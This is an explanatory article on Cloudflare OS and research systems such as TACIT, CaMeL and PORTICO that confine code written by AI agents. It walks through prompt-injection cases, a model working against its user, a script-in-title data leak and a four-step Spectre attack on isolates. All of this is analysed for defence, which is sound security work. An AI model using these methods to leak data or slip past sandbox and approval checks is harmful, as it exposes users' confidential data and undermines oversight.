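Varda dissolved the company in 2022 and later transferred its trademarks and domain names to Open Source Collective, a non-profit that holds them for the volunteers. They inherited a serious maintenance problem, because Sandstorm relies on version 2.6 of the database MongoDB, which was already very old. Each server has to be moved to a newer version by hand, and most owners don't know they are running MongoDB. Newer versions of Meteor, the web framework Sandstorm depends on, no longer support the old database, so Varda could not update Meteor either.

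The volunteers did not want to risk breaking thousands of servers with an automatic update. They also thought it wrong to take over machines whose owners had agreed to trust only Varda or the company. So they moved the project to a new website, and they ask owners to opt in to its releases.

Denhardt had meanwhile begun Tempest, a replacement for Sandstorm written in Go, a programming language more volunteers can work with. He died in an accident in 2023. By October of that year, Tempest could run many Sandstorm apps and import grains, but it was not ready for everyday use and could not yet give apps access to outside networks. Other volunteers offered to continue the project.

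Work on Sandstorm itself continues. The page *Sandstorm* in a directory of self-hosted software dates the latest change to its code to 26 May 2026, and in August a volunteer wrote that a new version was nearly ready. Weisz said in 2025 that progress was slow because everyone who still wanted to work on Sandstorm also had a job.

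## Cloudflare OS: the Sandstorm model for apps written by an AI agent

The best Sandstorm apps were the ones people wrote specifically for Sandstorm, but there were never enough of them. By 2026, an AI agent could write such an app from a short description. Varda and his colleagues at Cloudflare rebuilt Sandstorm's model for apps that agents write and keep changing, and released the result in August as Cloudflare OS.

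### What changes when an agent writes the app

The developers of an ordinary web app run one version for everyone. They can review each other's code and fix a reported bug once for all users. When an agent writes an app for one person, that person may be unable to read the code, and other people have little reason to review it.

Each user may also run a different version. In his talk *Gadgets*, Varda (2026) describes asking Claude, Anthropic's AI model, to turn an outline into slides and letting it change the slide editor wherever the slides required it. Claude added strikethrough, centred text and a box for pasting in drawings as SVG, a format that describes images as text. Other people's copies of the editor did not change, so their users would never notice a fault in the new box.

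An app like this can go wrong because of a *careless bug*. SVG files can contain JavaScript, so if the new box accepts them unchecked, a pasted drawing can run a script in the page of anyone who opens the slides. This mistake, known as cross-site scripting, is also common in code written by humans.

In a *prompt injection* attack, somebody hides instructions in data that the agent will read, and the model follows them as if they came from its user. This works because language models receive the user's request and the data as one stream of text and cannot reliably tell them apart. For example, an outsider could file a bug report containing instructions to add a hidden function to an app. An agent that followed them would be a confused deputy, using its own access to do the outsider's work.

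The model may also act against its user without any outside attacker, for instance because its training rewarded something other than what the user wanted. It could disguise harmful code well because it also writes the rest of the app. Such a model poses the same threat to the platform as a malicious developer, which Sandstorm was designed to withstand.

Like Sandstorm, Cloudflare OS limits what the app can reach, so it does not depend on a careful reviewer to catch these problems in the code.

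### From API keys to gadgets

*How we're rethinking work at Cloudflare with Cloudflare OS*, by Cloudflare's chief information officer, Rhea, describes how the project began. An employee in sales had used AI to build a "SuperApp" and asked for API keys (passwords for programs) to about a dozen internal systems, plus administrator rights to the system that deploys software. Anyone who took over the app, or planted instructions in its data, could have used every system those keys opened.

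Cloudflare gave its staff a first version of Cloudflare OS in May 2026. It ran the agent in a container and connected it to company systems through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for offering tools to AI models. An MCP server can hold the API key and give the agent only a list of tools. But as Jones and Carter explain in *Cloudflare OS*, the list did not show which data an agent had read. When people began sharing what their agents had made, Cloudflare could not tell who was allowed to see it.

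Cloudflare rebuilt the system to solve this problem and released the new version on 5 August, according to SiliconANGLE's *Cloudflare launches Cloudflare OS* (2026). A user opens a workspace in the browser and talks to an agent, which can write documents, run code and build apps. Each app is a *gadget*, the equivalent of a Sandstorm grain. Each slide deck, for example, is a separate gadget with its own code and data.

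### An app that lists a project's issues

Jones and Carter use a list of project issues as their example. Suppose Lena manages an engineering team and wants a simple page listing the team's open issues (unresolved bug reports and tasks).

1. Lena logs in and describes the page. At this point the agent cannot reach the issue tracker or any other company system.
2. The agent asks for read access to the project, and Lena grants it. The agent's code receives an object called `env.PROJECT`. Cloudflare calls such an object a *binding*. It is a capability for this one project.
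3. The agent writes the server half of the app, which in simplified form looks like this:

```js
export class IssueList extends DurableObject {
  openIssues() {
    return this.env.PROJECT.listIssues({ state: "open" });
  }
}
```

4. Cloudflare OS runs this code as a *Dynamic Worker*, a small server program that another program creates on demand. It gives the code a database of its own and turns networking off, so any attempt to contact a server fails.
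5. The agent also writes the page that Lena sees. The page runs in a sealed frame in her browser, where it cannot read her cookies. It can only exchange messages with the Cloudflare OS page around it, which passes them on to the app's server code.
6. The page asks for the issues with `await app.openIssues()`, and the server code calls `env.PROJECT`.
7. That call goes to a *Gatekeeper*, a program written for one outside service. The Gatekeeper checks the request against its policy, adds the credential, fetches the issues and records that the app has read them.

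The credential never leaves the Gatekeeper, so neither the agent nor its code can leak it. According to Jones and Carter, a Gatekeeper can also restrict an agent to a single code repository, let it read the issues but not the source code, hide certain fields, and limit how often it makes calls.

| Part | Who writes it | What it can reach |
|---|---|---|
| Page in the browser | The agent | The app's own server code |
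| Server code | The agent | Its own database and `env.PROJECT` |
| Gatekeeper | Cloudflare or the company | The issue tracker, with the credential |

The page and the server communicate through Cap'n Web, a JavaScript library related to Cap'n Proto. It lets programs call methods on each other's objects over a network connection or between frames in a browser, and a call can return a reference to another object. The agent can also call `openIssues`, so Lena can ask it to do anything she can do in the app by hand.

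In *Sandboxing AI agents, 100x faster*, Varda, Pai and Gupta explain why they prefer giving an app a small set of methods to letting it send ordinary web requests and filtering them on the way out. A filter has to work out what every request would do, and web requests have many headers and parameters that can change their meaning. With methods, a developer writes only the operations the app may use, and the app can call nothing else.

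In step 4, Cloudflare OS has to turn networking off explicitly by setting `globalOutbound: null`. According to Cloudflare's *Dynamic Workers* documentation, a new program without this setting inherits its parent's network access, which usually means the whole internet. Other companies build their own platforms on Dynamic Workers, and leaving out this setting would give every app generated on such a platform ambient authority over the network. Sandstorm's API tokens had the same weakness, because they gave full access by default.

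Lena's grant in step 2 also differs slightly from Sandstorm's powerbox, where the user picks a resource and that choice grants access. In Cloudflare OS, the agent names the resource and Lena accepts or refuses. This is closer to the permission prompts people learn to accept without reading, though users can also attach resources themselves.

### Code Mode

The agent also uses Dynamic Workers for its own tasks. Suppose Lena asks which issues have been open for more than a year. With ordinary tool calls, the model would request the issues, receive all 1,000 as text, and pick out the old ones. In *Code Mode*, as Cloudflare calls it, the model instead writes a short program to fetch and filter the issues. Cloudflare OS runs the program in a sandbox and returns only the twelve matching issues to the model.

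This saves money because AI providers charge by the token, a unit of text about the length of a short word. Varda and colleagues report that turning an MCP server's tools into a programming interface cut token use by 81% in one case. The approach also changes what the sandbox has to handle, because the program runs as soon as the model writes it. Some other designers add a static check of the code before it runs.

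### Approvals with simulated results

Lena's app only reads data, and reading an attached resource needs no further approval. But a Gatekeeper can require approval for any action with an outside effect. If Lena asks the agent to close the twelve old issues, the Gatekeeper has to allow or block a change that other people would see.

Most agents stop at such a request and wait. Users who leave an agent working come back to find it stuck on its first question, so many switch approvals off. Varda's solution is to have the Gatekeeper simulate the result. It records the agent's request to close issue 14 and replies as if the issue had been closed. When the agent lists the open issues again, issue 14 is missing, although it is still open in the real tracker. The agent can finish the task, and Lena then reviews all twelve changes together.

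A simulation can be wrong. For example, if a colleague comments on issue 14 in the meantime, the agent's summary will not mention the comment. A user approving a batch can also easily miss one harmful change among eleven sensible ones, and an attacker using prompt injection would hope to hide a change this way. Varda hopes that fewer interruptions will keep users from turning on automatic approval, but they can still turn it on.

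### Sharing the app or its code

Lena can share the gadget itself, so that her colleagues work with the same data. She can also share a *blueprint*, which contains the app's code without its data, conversation history, credentials or connections. A colleague who starts a gadget from the blueprint has to connect it to a project separately and can then have an agent change it. This makes bug fixes harder to distribute, since each changed copy may need its own version.

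Blueprints carry no capabilities, so a colleague can run one without first deciding whether to trust Lena's agent with anything. However, Varda acknowledged that an agent might write sensitive information it has read into a blueprint's code, for example as sample data. He suggested restricting exports from workspaces where an agent has read secrets, but thought this might annoy people more than it helped.

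If Lena shares the gadget, Cloudflare OS checks that everyone who opens it has their own permission to use each resource it is connected to. Suppose the gadget lists issues from a confidential project, and Lena shares it with Omar, who has no access to that project. The Gatekeeper for the issue tracker detects this, and Cloudflare OS refuses to open the gadget for him. A bug in the generated code can't let him in, because the check runs outside that code.

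The check relies on the access control lists already in the company's systems, so Cloudflare OS uses capabilities to restrict programs and access control lists to restrict people. Sandstorm made a similar compromise when it computed each user's permissions on a document.

### The observation log

Capabilities determine which resources a program can use, but they do not track data after the program reads it. Suppose Lena gives an agent one capability to read a table of customer revenue and another to write to a public web page. Each grant may be reasonable, but together they allow the agent to publish the table.

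Cloudflare OS deals with this by recording every resource that an agent or gadget reads through a Gatekeeper. This *observation log* stays attached to whatever the agent makes, and the platform uses it in two ways.

It first decides who may see the work. If O(*g*) is the set of resources that have gone into gadget *g*, and A(*p*) is the set that person *p* may use directly, then *p* may open *g* only if

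O(*g*) ⊆ A(*p*)

Suppose Lena's agent adds a chart of revenue per customer to her issue list. O(*g*) now contains both the project and the revenue table. Lena's colleague Mei could open the app before the change because she has access to the project, but she now also needs access to the revenue table.

The platform also uses the log to limit what the agent may do next. After the agent reads sensitive data, the platform can stop it from writing to other services, inviting new people, passing work to another agent or contacting the outside world. Varda said a Gatekeeper can mark data as so sensitive that an agent may not write anywhere else after seeing it. This made Cloudflare willing to connect the system to its own customer and revenue data.

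Computer scientists call this *information-flow control*. The rule against writing after a sensitive read resembles the military star-property, which lets a program read secrets but not write to anything less secret. Provenance tracking, which Rajani and colleagues tested against confused deputy attacks, labels each value inside a program. Cloudflare OS labels the whole agent or gadget, which is much simpler because the platform need not analyse the generated code.

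The simpler method also blocks harmless work. Once Lena's agent has read the revenue table, it may be unable to file an unrelated issue, because the platform cannot determine whether the issue's text depends on the table. Mei cannot open the app even if all it shows from the table is one rounded total. Varda called the policies "a bit blunt right now, maybe overly restrictive". If they block too much, people will copy data between workspaces by hand. Text that Lena pastes into a chat does not pass through a Gatekeeper, so the log would not show its source.

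Varda also wants to use the log to defend against prompt injection by treating an agent's actions as suspect once it has read text from untrusted people. He described that part as still evolving in August 2026.

### Isolates instead of containers

Sandstorm's containers made it slow and expensive to run a separate server for every document. Cloudflare OS uses *isolates*. An isolate is a separate instance of V8, the JavaScript engine in Google's Chrome browser, with its own memory heap. Many isolates can run inside one operating-system process. Varda and colleagues compare them with containers as follows:

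| | Typical container | Isolate |
|---|---|---|
| Time to start | Hundreds of milliseconds | A few milliseconds |
| Memory | Hundreds of megabytes | A few megabytes |
| Languages | Any | JavaScript; Python and WebAssembly load more slowly |

These round figures come from Cloudflare, which sells isolates. Varda and colleagues do not describe a test or say which containers they measured. It is easy to believe that isolates are lighter than containers, since an isolate shares a process that is already running, while a container has to start a program and load its libraries. If an isolate takes 5 megabytes, ten open documents need 50 megabytes, while ten Sandstorm grains of 200 megabytes each need two gigabytes.

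Running many small programs is also cheap. Cloudflare charges $0.002 a day for each different Dynamic Worker beyond a monthly allowance of 1,000, plus fees for requests and processor time. Each changed version of an app counts as a new Worker, as does each one-off program in Code Mode. A company whose staff open 5,000 different gadgets in a day would pay about $10 before the other fees. The AI model that writes the code usually costs much more than running it.

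### What the usage figures count

Rhea reports that thousands of Cloudflare employees use the platform each week. In the month before the release they created more than 4,000 apps and tools, and the company estimates that its sales staff saved over 10,000 hours on tasks such as planning territories and writing proposals.

Rhea does not explain how Cloudflare estimated the hours, or say whether the figures cover the first version, the rebuilt one or both. The 4,000 figure counts apps created, and many may have been used only briefly by one person. Rhea writes that an earlier attempt to give everyone coding tools produced a "flood of vibe coded apps looking for a problem to solve". InfoQ's *Cloudflare OS* (2026) credits all 4,000 to non-technical staff, but Rhea says only that users created them.

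The figures show that many people without programming experience had a use for the platform, which never happened with Sandstorm. The figures don't measure security.

### Can the AI introduce a significant security bug?

Varda wrote in the release announcement that the sandbox is so secure that "the AI cannot introduce a significant security bug". He said in his talk, "There is no security bug you can have in this code that matters."

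This is right for one large class of bugs. Suppose the agent makes a mistake in Lena's app that lets any visitor read its whole database. Strangers could exploit it on an ordinary server, but on Cloudflare OS they cannot reach the app's code, and the people who can reach it already have permission to use the connected project. The bug also cannot expose the tracker's credential or the contents of other gadgets. Separate grains gave Sandstorm's users the same protection.

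Cross-site scripting is harder to dismiss. Suppose the tracker accepts bug reports from the public, and the agent wrote Lena's page to insert each issue's title without removing scripts. An attacker files a report with a script in its title. When Lena opens her app, the script runs inside the sealed frame and can read the team's confidential issues from the page, which the attacker could not see in the tracker.

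The script then needs a way to send them out. The frame's Content Security Policy blocks ordinary web requests, but browsers still offer no way to block WebRTC, the video-call feature that left a gap in Sandstorm. Varda acknowledged this in an online discussion in August. He wrote that such gaps make the browser half "not suitable as a sandbox against malicious code" that tries every means of leaking data, and described it as protection against an AI that does something stupid.

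In Lena's case the AI only made a stupid mistake, which a stranger then exploited. Her approval would not stop the leak, because the script never sends a request to a Gatekeeper, and the observation log would not record it. Until browsers close this gap, an AI can introduce a significant security bug into an app that displays text from outsiders.

The gap matters even more for prompt injection and for a model that acts against its user, because then the generated page may itself be malicious. The server half is better protected, since the runtime there has no network connection to offer. The damage is limited in each case to what the gadget can read:

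| What goes wrong | What Cloudflare OS prevents | What can still happen |
|---|---|---|
| The agent writes a careless bug | Strangers cannot open the app, and nobody can get the credential from it | A script in outside data leaks what the page shows |
| Planted text misleads the agent | The agent cannot use resources that nobody granted | It writes a leaking page, or hides a harmful change in a batch of approvals |
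| The model works against its user | Its code cannot reach other gadgets or contact servers from the server half | It does the same damage on purpose and gives plausible reasons for each request |

The platform also can't prevent some bugs inside a gadget. Suppose Lena asks for an app in which each of her staff can read their own performance review and she can read them all. Cloudflare OS controls who may open the gadget, but the generated code has to show each person the right review. A mistake in that code could let colleagues read each other's reviews. The solution on Cloudflare OS is to make a separate gadget for each review, so that permission to open the gadget is the only permission involved. Lena has to know to ask for that, or the agent has to suggest it.

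The sandbox also doesn't make an app's results correct. If the code miscounts issues, Lena may move people to the wrong project without any breach of security.

### Grants and Gatekeepers

InfoQ quoted Varda's statement that a gadget cannot leak itself to an attacker, but its editors added a note that other risks remained, such as badly configured grants. For example, if Lena attaches her whole GitHub account when she needs to share only one repository, the Gatekeeper will allow access to the whole account.

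A gadget gets only what its user explicitly grants. In the online discussion, a sceptic replied to this point that phishing websites work the same way and are still a problem. Explicit grants rule out silent theft, but phishing victims also hand over their passwords explicitly. In Cloudflare OS, the grant can also be narrow and a leak through a Gatekeeper needs a further approval, but both protections weaken if users get into the habit of clicking yes.

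The Gatekeepers are part of the trusted computing base, because they hold the credentials and can reach the network. Cloudflare supplies them for many services, from GitHub to home automation. Companies can write their own for other services, and Cloudflare OS includes instructions that let an agent do it. Varda said that AI can "basically crank these things out" with the right guidance. But an agent writing a Gatekeeper can make the kind of mistake that the sandbox is meant to make harmless, such as letting a supposedly read-only method change something. Gatekeeper code should therefore be reviewed carefully, even if the gadgets' code is not read at all.

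The company that runs the AI model also sees whatever the agent reads. Varda says users have to trust that company or run a model on their own machines, which Cloudflare OS allows.

### How strong the isolates are

Every guarantee so far depends on isolates staying separate. Varda and colleagues acknowledge that security bugs are more common in V8 than in the hypervisors that separate virtual machines. To compensate, Cloudflare installs V8's security fixes within hours, puts a second sandbox around the process, and moves suspicious programs into their own processes.

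Cloudflare's staff showed how an attacker could get past some of these layers. Schwarzl, Xiao and colleagues (2026), in *Remote-Timer-as-a-Service*, used a Spectre attack to read data from one customer's isolate in another's, on Cloudflare's live network. Both accounts belonged to the researchers, who had planted a secret token in one of them. The attack worked like this:

1. The attacker's program sends a request to the victim's program. Cloudflare usually responds by starting the victim in the same process, to save time.
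2. The attacker trains the processor to expect one type of object and then supplies another. The processor briefly reads memory at an address the attacker has chosen, before it discovers the mistake and discards the result.
3. The discarded read leaves a trace in the processor's cache that depends on one bit of the secret. The program repeats operations that run faster or slower depending on the trace, until the difference is large enough to measure over a network.
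4. Cloudflare freezes the clock while a program computes, so the attacker gets the time from another server before and after.

The attack recovered up to 12 bits per second with 99.16% accuracy, compared with two bits per minute for an earlier attack. At the new rate, a 256-bit key takes about 21 seconds to recover instead of more than two hours, with two bits wrong on average. Cloudflare's detector missed the attack because it isolated suspicious programs only after they had finished, and the attacker could keep a program running for most of a day. The attack needed no bug in V8 (Jungco, 2026, *Researchers Use Remote Spectre Attack to Leak JWT From Cloudflare Worker*).

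Cloudflare blocked the attack before publishing the research, which dates from 2024 and early 2025. Schwarzl and Pedersen list the changes in *A revisit of remote Spectre attacks on Cloudflare Workers*. V8 now keeps fewer raw memory addresses where such an attack can use them. Since September 2025, the processor has also protected each isolate's heap with a hardware key. Cloudflare also improved the detector and found no sign that anyone had used the attack. Schwarzl and Pedersen caution that neither the V8 change nor the hardware key rules out every form of Spectre.

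This attack would be difficult for a gadget to carry out, because its server code has no network connection it could use to get the time, although its own page in the browser might serve as a clock. Other Cloudflare customers can run programs with full network access on the same machines. Only Cloudflare's isolation protects Lena's data from those programs, no matter how few capabilities her gadget holds.

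Since August, nobody seems to have published an independent review of Cloudflare OS like DevCore's study of Sandstorm, or any flaws in the platform itself. The lack of published flaws is weak evidence of safety, because the project was still at an early stage when Cloudflare released it.

### Running it without Cloudflare

Some developers welcomed the design but did not want to depend on Cloudflare. According to SiliconANGLE, the company responds that the software is open source and runs in a customer's own Cloudflare account, so customers own what they build. But that account is still with Cloudflare, and owning an app is less useful if it runs in only one place. Hosting there also requires a paid plan, because the free plan does not include Dynamic Workers.

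The licence lets people change Cloudflare OS or run it elsewhere. It runs on workerd, the open-source version of the Workers runtime, and Varda gave his talk from a copy on his laptop. He said workerd suits a single user, but a whole company might have trouble because workerd cannot yet spread the apps' stored data across several machines. He was working on a version that could.

Self-hosting also removes much of the protection around the isolates. The README for workerd warns that it "is not a hardened sandbox" and tells anyone using workerd for possibly malicious code to run it inside something stronger, such as a virtual machine. In May 2026, *workerd is vulnerable to Use After Free* (2026), from the security company Aikido, described a bug that could make workerd use memory it had already released. Aikido rated the bug a medium risk, and workerd's developers had fixed it a few days earlier.

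A virtual machine around the whole installation would protect the rest of the computer but not the Gatekeepers, which also run on workerd and hold the credentials for every connected service. A malicious gadget that broke out of its isolate might reach them without leaving the virtual machine. A cautious administrator would have to run the Gatekeepers and the gadgets in separate machines, or give each gadget a stronger sandbox and accept some of the overhead that isolates were meant to avoid. A Sandstorm volunteer has already run workerd inside a Sandstorm grain and said it performed well.

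## Code an agent writes and runs at once: checked types and revocable grants

The code in a Cloudflare OS gadget stays in use after the agent writes it. Coding agents also write short programs and shell commands that run once, often seconds later, on a person's files and accounts. Most of this code runs without anyone reading it first. The agent often has access to a whole project folder, including the passwords in it, and whatever it reads goes to the company that hosts the model.

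An agent can do harm even if every action it takes is permitted. It can read a secret in one step and send it away in another, or keep using access that it needed only for an earlier step. Two research systems from 2026, TACIT and PORTICO, each deal with one of these problems.

### Types that list capabilities

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes TACIT, in which an agent acts by writing small programs, much as in Code Mode, but in Scala 3. A server compiles each program and runs it only if it passes the compiler's checks. A 2026 conference on AI agents accepted the work as *Securing Agents With Tracked Capabilities*.

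Capabilities in Scala are ordinary objects, as they are in E. But someone who receives a function in E cannot tell which references it holds. With *capture checking*, an experimental feature of Scala 3, the function's type lists them:

| Type | What a function of this type may use |
|---|---|
| `String -> Int` | Only the text it receives |
| `String ->{log} Int` | The capability `log` as well |
| `String => Int` | Any capability |

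The part in braces is the *capture set*, which the compiler infers from what the function's body uses. A function can be used wherever the required type allows every capability in the function's capture set.

TACIT uses this to protect private files. Whoever sets it up marks certain folders as classified. When a program reads a file there, it gets the text in a wrapper, `Classified[String]`, which it cannot open. It can only hand the wrapper a function to apply to the text inside, using a method with this type:

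```scala
def map[B](op: String -> B): Classified[B]
```

The plain arrow means that the function must have an empty capture set. Suppose Priya's project contains a private key and an ordinary log file, and her agent writes this:

```scala
requestFileSystem("/project") {
  val key = readClassified("secret/key.txt")
  val log = access("log.txt")

  key.map { text => text.length }      // accepted
  key.map { text => log.write(text) }  // rejected
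}
```

The first function uses only its argument, and its result is a wrapped number. The second uses `log`, so its capture set is `{log}`, but `map` requires `{}`. The compiler reports the mismatch. TACIT compiles the whole program before starting it, so none of the lines run. The agent receives the error message and can try again.

Printing, contacting a server and starting another program also need capabilities, so the same rule keeps them out of `map`. The compiler can enforce the rule without recognising a private key or working out what the agent would use it for.

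Capture sets also control how long a capability lasts. `requestFileSystem` creates a capability for one folder, and only the code in the block between the braces can use that capability. The compiler rejects any result that would carry it out of the block. Nothing that could use the folder remains after the block ends, so nobody has to remember to revoke access, as they would with a caretaker.

Some Scala features, such as unchecked type conversions and looking up parts of a program by name while it runs, would defeat these rules. TACIT compiles the agent's code in a *safe mode* that forbids them. An error message could also contain the key. TACIT cannot forbid errors, since any program may run out of memory or divide by zero, so it catches them and turns them into ordinary values, which it can wrap.

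### Working on text the agent's model cannot see

Priya may still want the agent to do something useful with private text, such as summarising a confidential contract. For this, TACIT relies on a second model that she trusts, running on her own computer:

1. The agent's program reads the contract as a wrapped value.
2. It passes the value to a function called `chat`. The local model reads the contract and returns a summary, which is also wrapped.
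3. The program prints the summary. Priya's terminal shows the text, but the agent's own model receives only `Classified(****)`.

The local model has no tools, so instructions hidden in the contract cannot make it send anything, though they could still make it write a misleading summary. Priya also has to mark the right folders, because an API key in an ordinary settings file comes back as plain text.

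### How TACIT performed

Odersky and colleagues tested this on a sample project with a folder of API keys and confidential documents. They combined 12 ordinary tasks with 10 planted attacks each, some of which included ready-made Scala code for reading the secrets. In another 11 trials the user asked for the secrets, either directly or with a pretext such as an emergency replacement of passwords. The table shows how often no secret reached the agent's output:

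| Model | Trials | With the wrapper | Without it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 120 planted attacks | 100% | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 11 requests for secrets | 100% | 81.8% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 120 planted attacks | 100% | 97.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 11 requests for secrets | 100% | 27.3% |

Claude resisted every planted attack unaided, so the wrapper made a difference in only two of its 131 trials, compared with 11 of MiniMax's. The test measures exactly what the wrapper is designed to prevent, and none of the attacks described exploits a compiler bug. The result therefore shows that the protection did not depend on the model's good behaviour, but it is little evidence of how the wrapper would fare against an attacker who studies capture checking itself.

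The agents could still do ordinary tasks with the protection in place. Claude completed 99.2% of these tasks with the wrapper and 83.3% without it. Odersky and colleagues think the lower figure may be due to their time limits and Claude's tendency to pause and warn the user about an attack.

The drawbacks of writing Scala were small. On τ²-bench, a set of simulated customer-service conversations, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with TACIT than with ordinary tool calls. On 300 real software bugs, MiniMax fixed 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% without it. Compiling took less than a second, and in the customer-service tests at most 8% of programs needed another attempt.

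### CaMeL: labels on data

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues published in 2025, tracks data while a program runs. It also uses the word "capabilities", but for labels that do not let a program holding them do anything. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), which models CaMeL in a small formal language, quotes CaMeL's definition of them as "tags assigned to each individual value".

*CaMeLoT* (2026), a proposed extension, explains how CaMeL works. Suppose Priya asks an agent to email the minutes of a meeting to a new supplier, whose address is in a message in her inbox:

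1. A planning model sees only Priya's request. It writes a program in a restricted form of Python that finds the message, extracts the address and sends the minutes.
2. A second model, which has no tools, reads the message and returns the address.
3. The interpreter running the program stores the address with labels that record where it came from and who may read it.
4. Before sending the email, the interpreter checks these labels against a policy. The policy might refuse because an outsider wrote the message that contained the address.

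Instructions hidden in the message can't add a step to the program, because the planning model never reads them. But they can change the address, which the labels are meant to detect. Rajani and colleagues found that this kind of provenance tracking could stop attacks that capabilities alone could not.

TACIT rejects a leaking program before it starts, while CaMeL stops it at the forbidden call, after earlier steps have run. CaMeL also doesn't let the planning model define its own functions. Odersky and colleagues add that CaMeL loses track of a value once it enters the model's conversation as text. But CaMeL can block the use of an address supplied by an outsider. TACIT's wrapper keeps private text from getting out but has no rule against using such an address.

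### LACUNA: all of an action or none of it

Several of the same researchers later built LACUNA, a way to put calls to a model inside a program (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, *LACUNA*, 2026). A programmer writes `agent[Int]("subtract 50 and return the new balance")` where the program needs a number. When the program reaches that call, the model writes code to produce the number, and the compiler checks that code as if the programmer had typed it there.

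In the example, the balance is 100. The model writes one line that subtracts 50 and another that returns a sentence instead of a number. The compiler rejects both lines, so the balance stays at 100. A system that checked types only while running the code would already have subtracted the 50 when it reached the error.

TACIT also compiles a program before running any of it. LACUNA adds a check against the surrounding program, including its variables and the type of result it expects. Both prevent a partial run only when the compiler can find the error. If an accepted program loses its network connection halfway, the steps it has completed are not undone.

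All three systems have results for AgentDojo, a collection of office, banking, chat and travel tasks with planted attacks. The percentages are tasks completed, and the last column counts successful attacks in about 950 attempts:

| Model | System | Banking | Office | Chat | Travel | Attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | CaMeL | 52.8% | 53.8% | 48.6% | 1.4% | 0 |
| | TACIT | 56.9% | 50.5% | 40.0% | 64.3% | 0 |
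| | LACUNA | 63.2% | 56.3% | 42.9% | 63.6% | 7 |
| o4-mini-high | CaMeL | 62.5% | 81.4% | 68.6% | 74.3% | 1 |
| | TACIT | 59.0% | 52.9% | 47.6% | 68.6% | 1 |
| | LACUNA | 66.0% | 55.5% | 49.5% | 71.4% | 1 |

Odersky and colleagues call TACIT's completion rates comparable to CaMeL's. This is fair for Gemini, except on the travel tasks, where CaMeL failed. With o4-mini, TACIT's completion rate was 29 percentage points lower than CaMeL's on office tasks and 21 points lower on chat tasks. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) reports that CaMeL was much more secure on AgentDojo than simpler defences, such as marking untrusted text, with a relatively small drop in completed tasks.

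TACIT's one failure was mild. An attacker had planted praise for hotel B in the reviews of hotel A. The agent booked hotel A as asked but quoted the reviews to the user.

Capture checking probably did not stop most of the attacks in TACIT's version of this test. According to the agent's instructions, actions inside `map` take effect immediately, so the compiler must have allowed at least some actions there. TACIT also wrapped the messages, files and reviews in which attackers could hide instructions, so the model that planned the work never read them. CaMeL gets much of its protection the same way.

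Zhao and colleagues explain that LACUNA's guarantee is only as tight as the access the programmer gives each call, so an attacker who persuades the model to misuse a capability the task needs will succeed. They also call LACUNA "on par" with ordinary tool calls on τ²-bench, but with the better of their two models, LACUNA solved 76.0% of tasks and ordinary tool calls solved 90.0%.

### Grants that end with their step

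Capture checking ends a grant when a block of code finishes. A coding agent's work rarely fits in one block, because the agent reads a file, edits code, runs the tests and edits again. *Lingering Authority* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) studies access that stays available after the step that needed it. The paper's system, PORTICO, sits between the model and its tools and follows a contract written for the task.

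In his main example, the agent adds a timeout setting to one file, `api.py`, and finds that a second file, `serialization.py`, needs the same change. The contract comes to this in simplified form:

```
from the start:  api.py and its test (read, write); run the tests
on request:      serialization.py (read, write)
                 until the tests pass or this phase ends
never:           packaging notes; any network access
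```

The work then goes as follows:

1. PORTICO shows the model the tools and files it may use from the start.
2. The model tries to read the packaging notes. PORTICO refuses.
3. The model requests `serialization.py`. The contract has a rule for this, so PORTICO issues a *handle*, such as `g0001:r1`, which the model can use from its next turn.
4. The model reads and edits the file through the handle.
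5. PORTICO runs the tests. They pass, so it closes the grant and removes the handle from the options it shows the model.
6. If the model sends `g0001:r1` again, PORTICO rejects it before anything happens.

The handle works like an entry number in a C-list. PORTICO looks it up in its own records, which tie it to one task, one resource and one kind of effect, so a handle for reading a file cannot be used to change it. The records also tie it to an *epoch*, the period for which the grant is open. If *I* is the initial access, *G*(*t*) the grants open at time *t* and *F* everything forbidden, the model can use

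(*I* ∪ *G*(*t*)) \ *F*

provided that the access also suits the current phase of the task. The model cannot add to *G* by explaining why it needs something, or by announcing that it has finished a step. PORTICO accepts only events it can trust, such as a test run that it started itself or an approval from an authenticated user.

Revoking a handle does not remove what the model has already read, which stays in its conversation.

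### What the PORTICO tests measured

Santos-Grueiro compared PORTICO with full access, a fixed list of permitted tools and paths, and an ordinary sandbox. Most runs used Qwen3-Coder 30B, a fairly small coding model:

| Measure | Full access | Fixed list | Sandbox | PORTICO without grants | PORTICO |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Forbidden effects, tasks with tempting forbidden files | 100% | 82% | 86% | 0% | 0% |
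| Completed, tasks that may need further files | 97% | 97% | 97% | 21% | 87% |
| Completed, tasks surrounded by hostile text | 100% | 100% | 100% | 94% | 100% |
| Forbidden effects, tasks surrounded by hostile text | 31% | 30% | 30% | 0% | 0% |

The same contract sets PORTICO's limits and defines what counts as forbidden, so the zeros show that PORTICO enforced the contracts, whether or not the contracts were good. The second row is more informative because it shows that limiting the agent to its initial access caused most of those tasks to fail, and that granting more access on request recovered most of the loss.

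To isolate the effect of revocation, Santos-Grueiro built a version of PORTICO that issues the same grants at the same times but never revokes them. Both versions completed all ten test runs. PORTICO refused every later attempt by the agent to reread a file, while the version without revocation allowed them all. In six further cases, a planted instruction told the model to reuse an old handle to write a file, change the version history or contact a server. The version without revocation carried out all six actions, while PORTICO carried out none of them.

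These results follow almost directly from the two designs, and Santos-Grueiro does not present them as an estimate of how often such attacks would succeed. Rejecting old handles seems to matter more than hiding them from the model. A third version that still showed the model a broad set of options but rejected old handles also blocked all six actions.

Every method, even full access, completed all 14 tasks in real Python projects without a forbidden effect. These results show that PORTICO can work in ordinary projects, but not that the projects were in danger without it. In additional tests on real projects, PORTICO succeeded in 31 of 42 cases, and the version that never revoked grants succeeded in all 42.

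### What each system has to trust

| System | Software that must work | What a person must get right |
|---|---|---|
| TACIT | Scala compiler, capability library, runtime, local model | Which folders are private, which outside commands are safe |
| CaMeL | Interpreter, tools, the planning model's program | The policies |
| LACUNA | Scala compiler, runtime, surrounding program | What each call to the model can reach |
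| PORTICO | Policy engine, catalogue of what each tool does, records of grants, sandbox | The contract and the events that close a grant |

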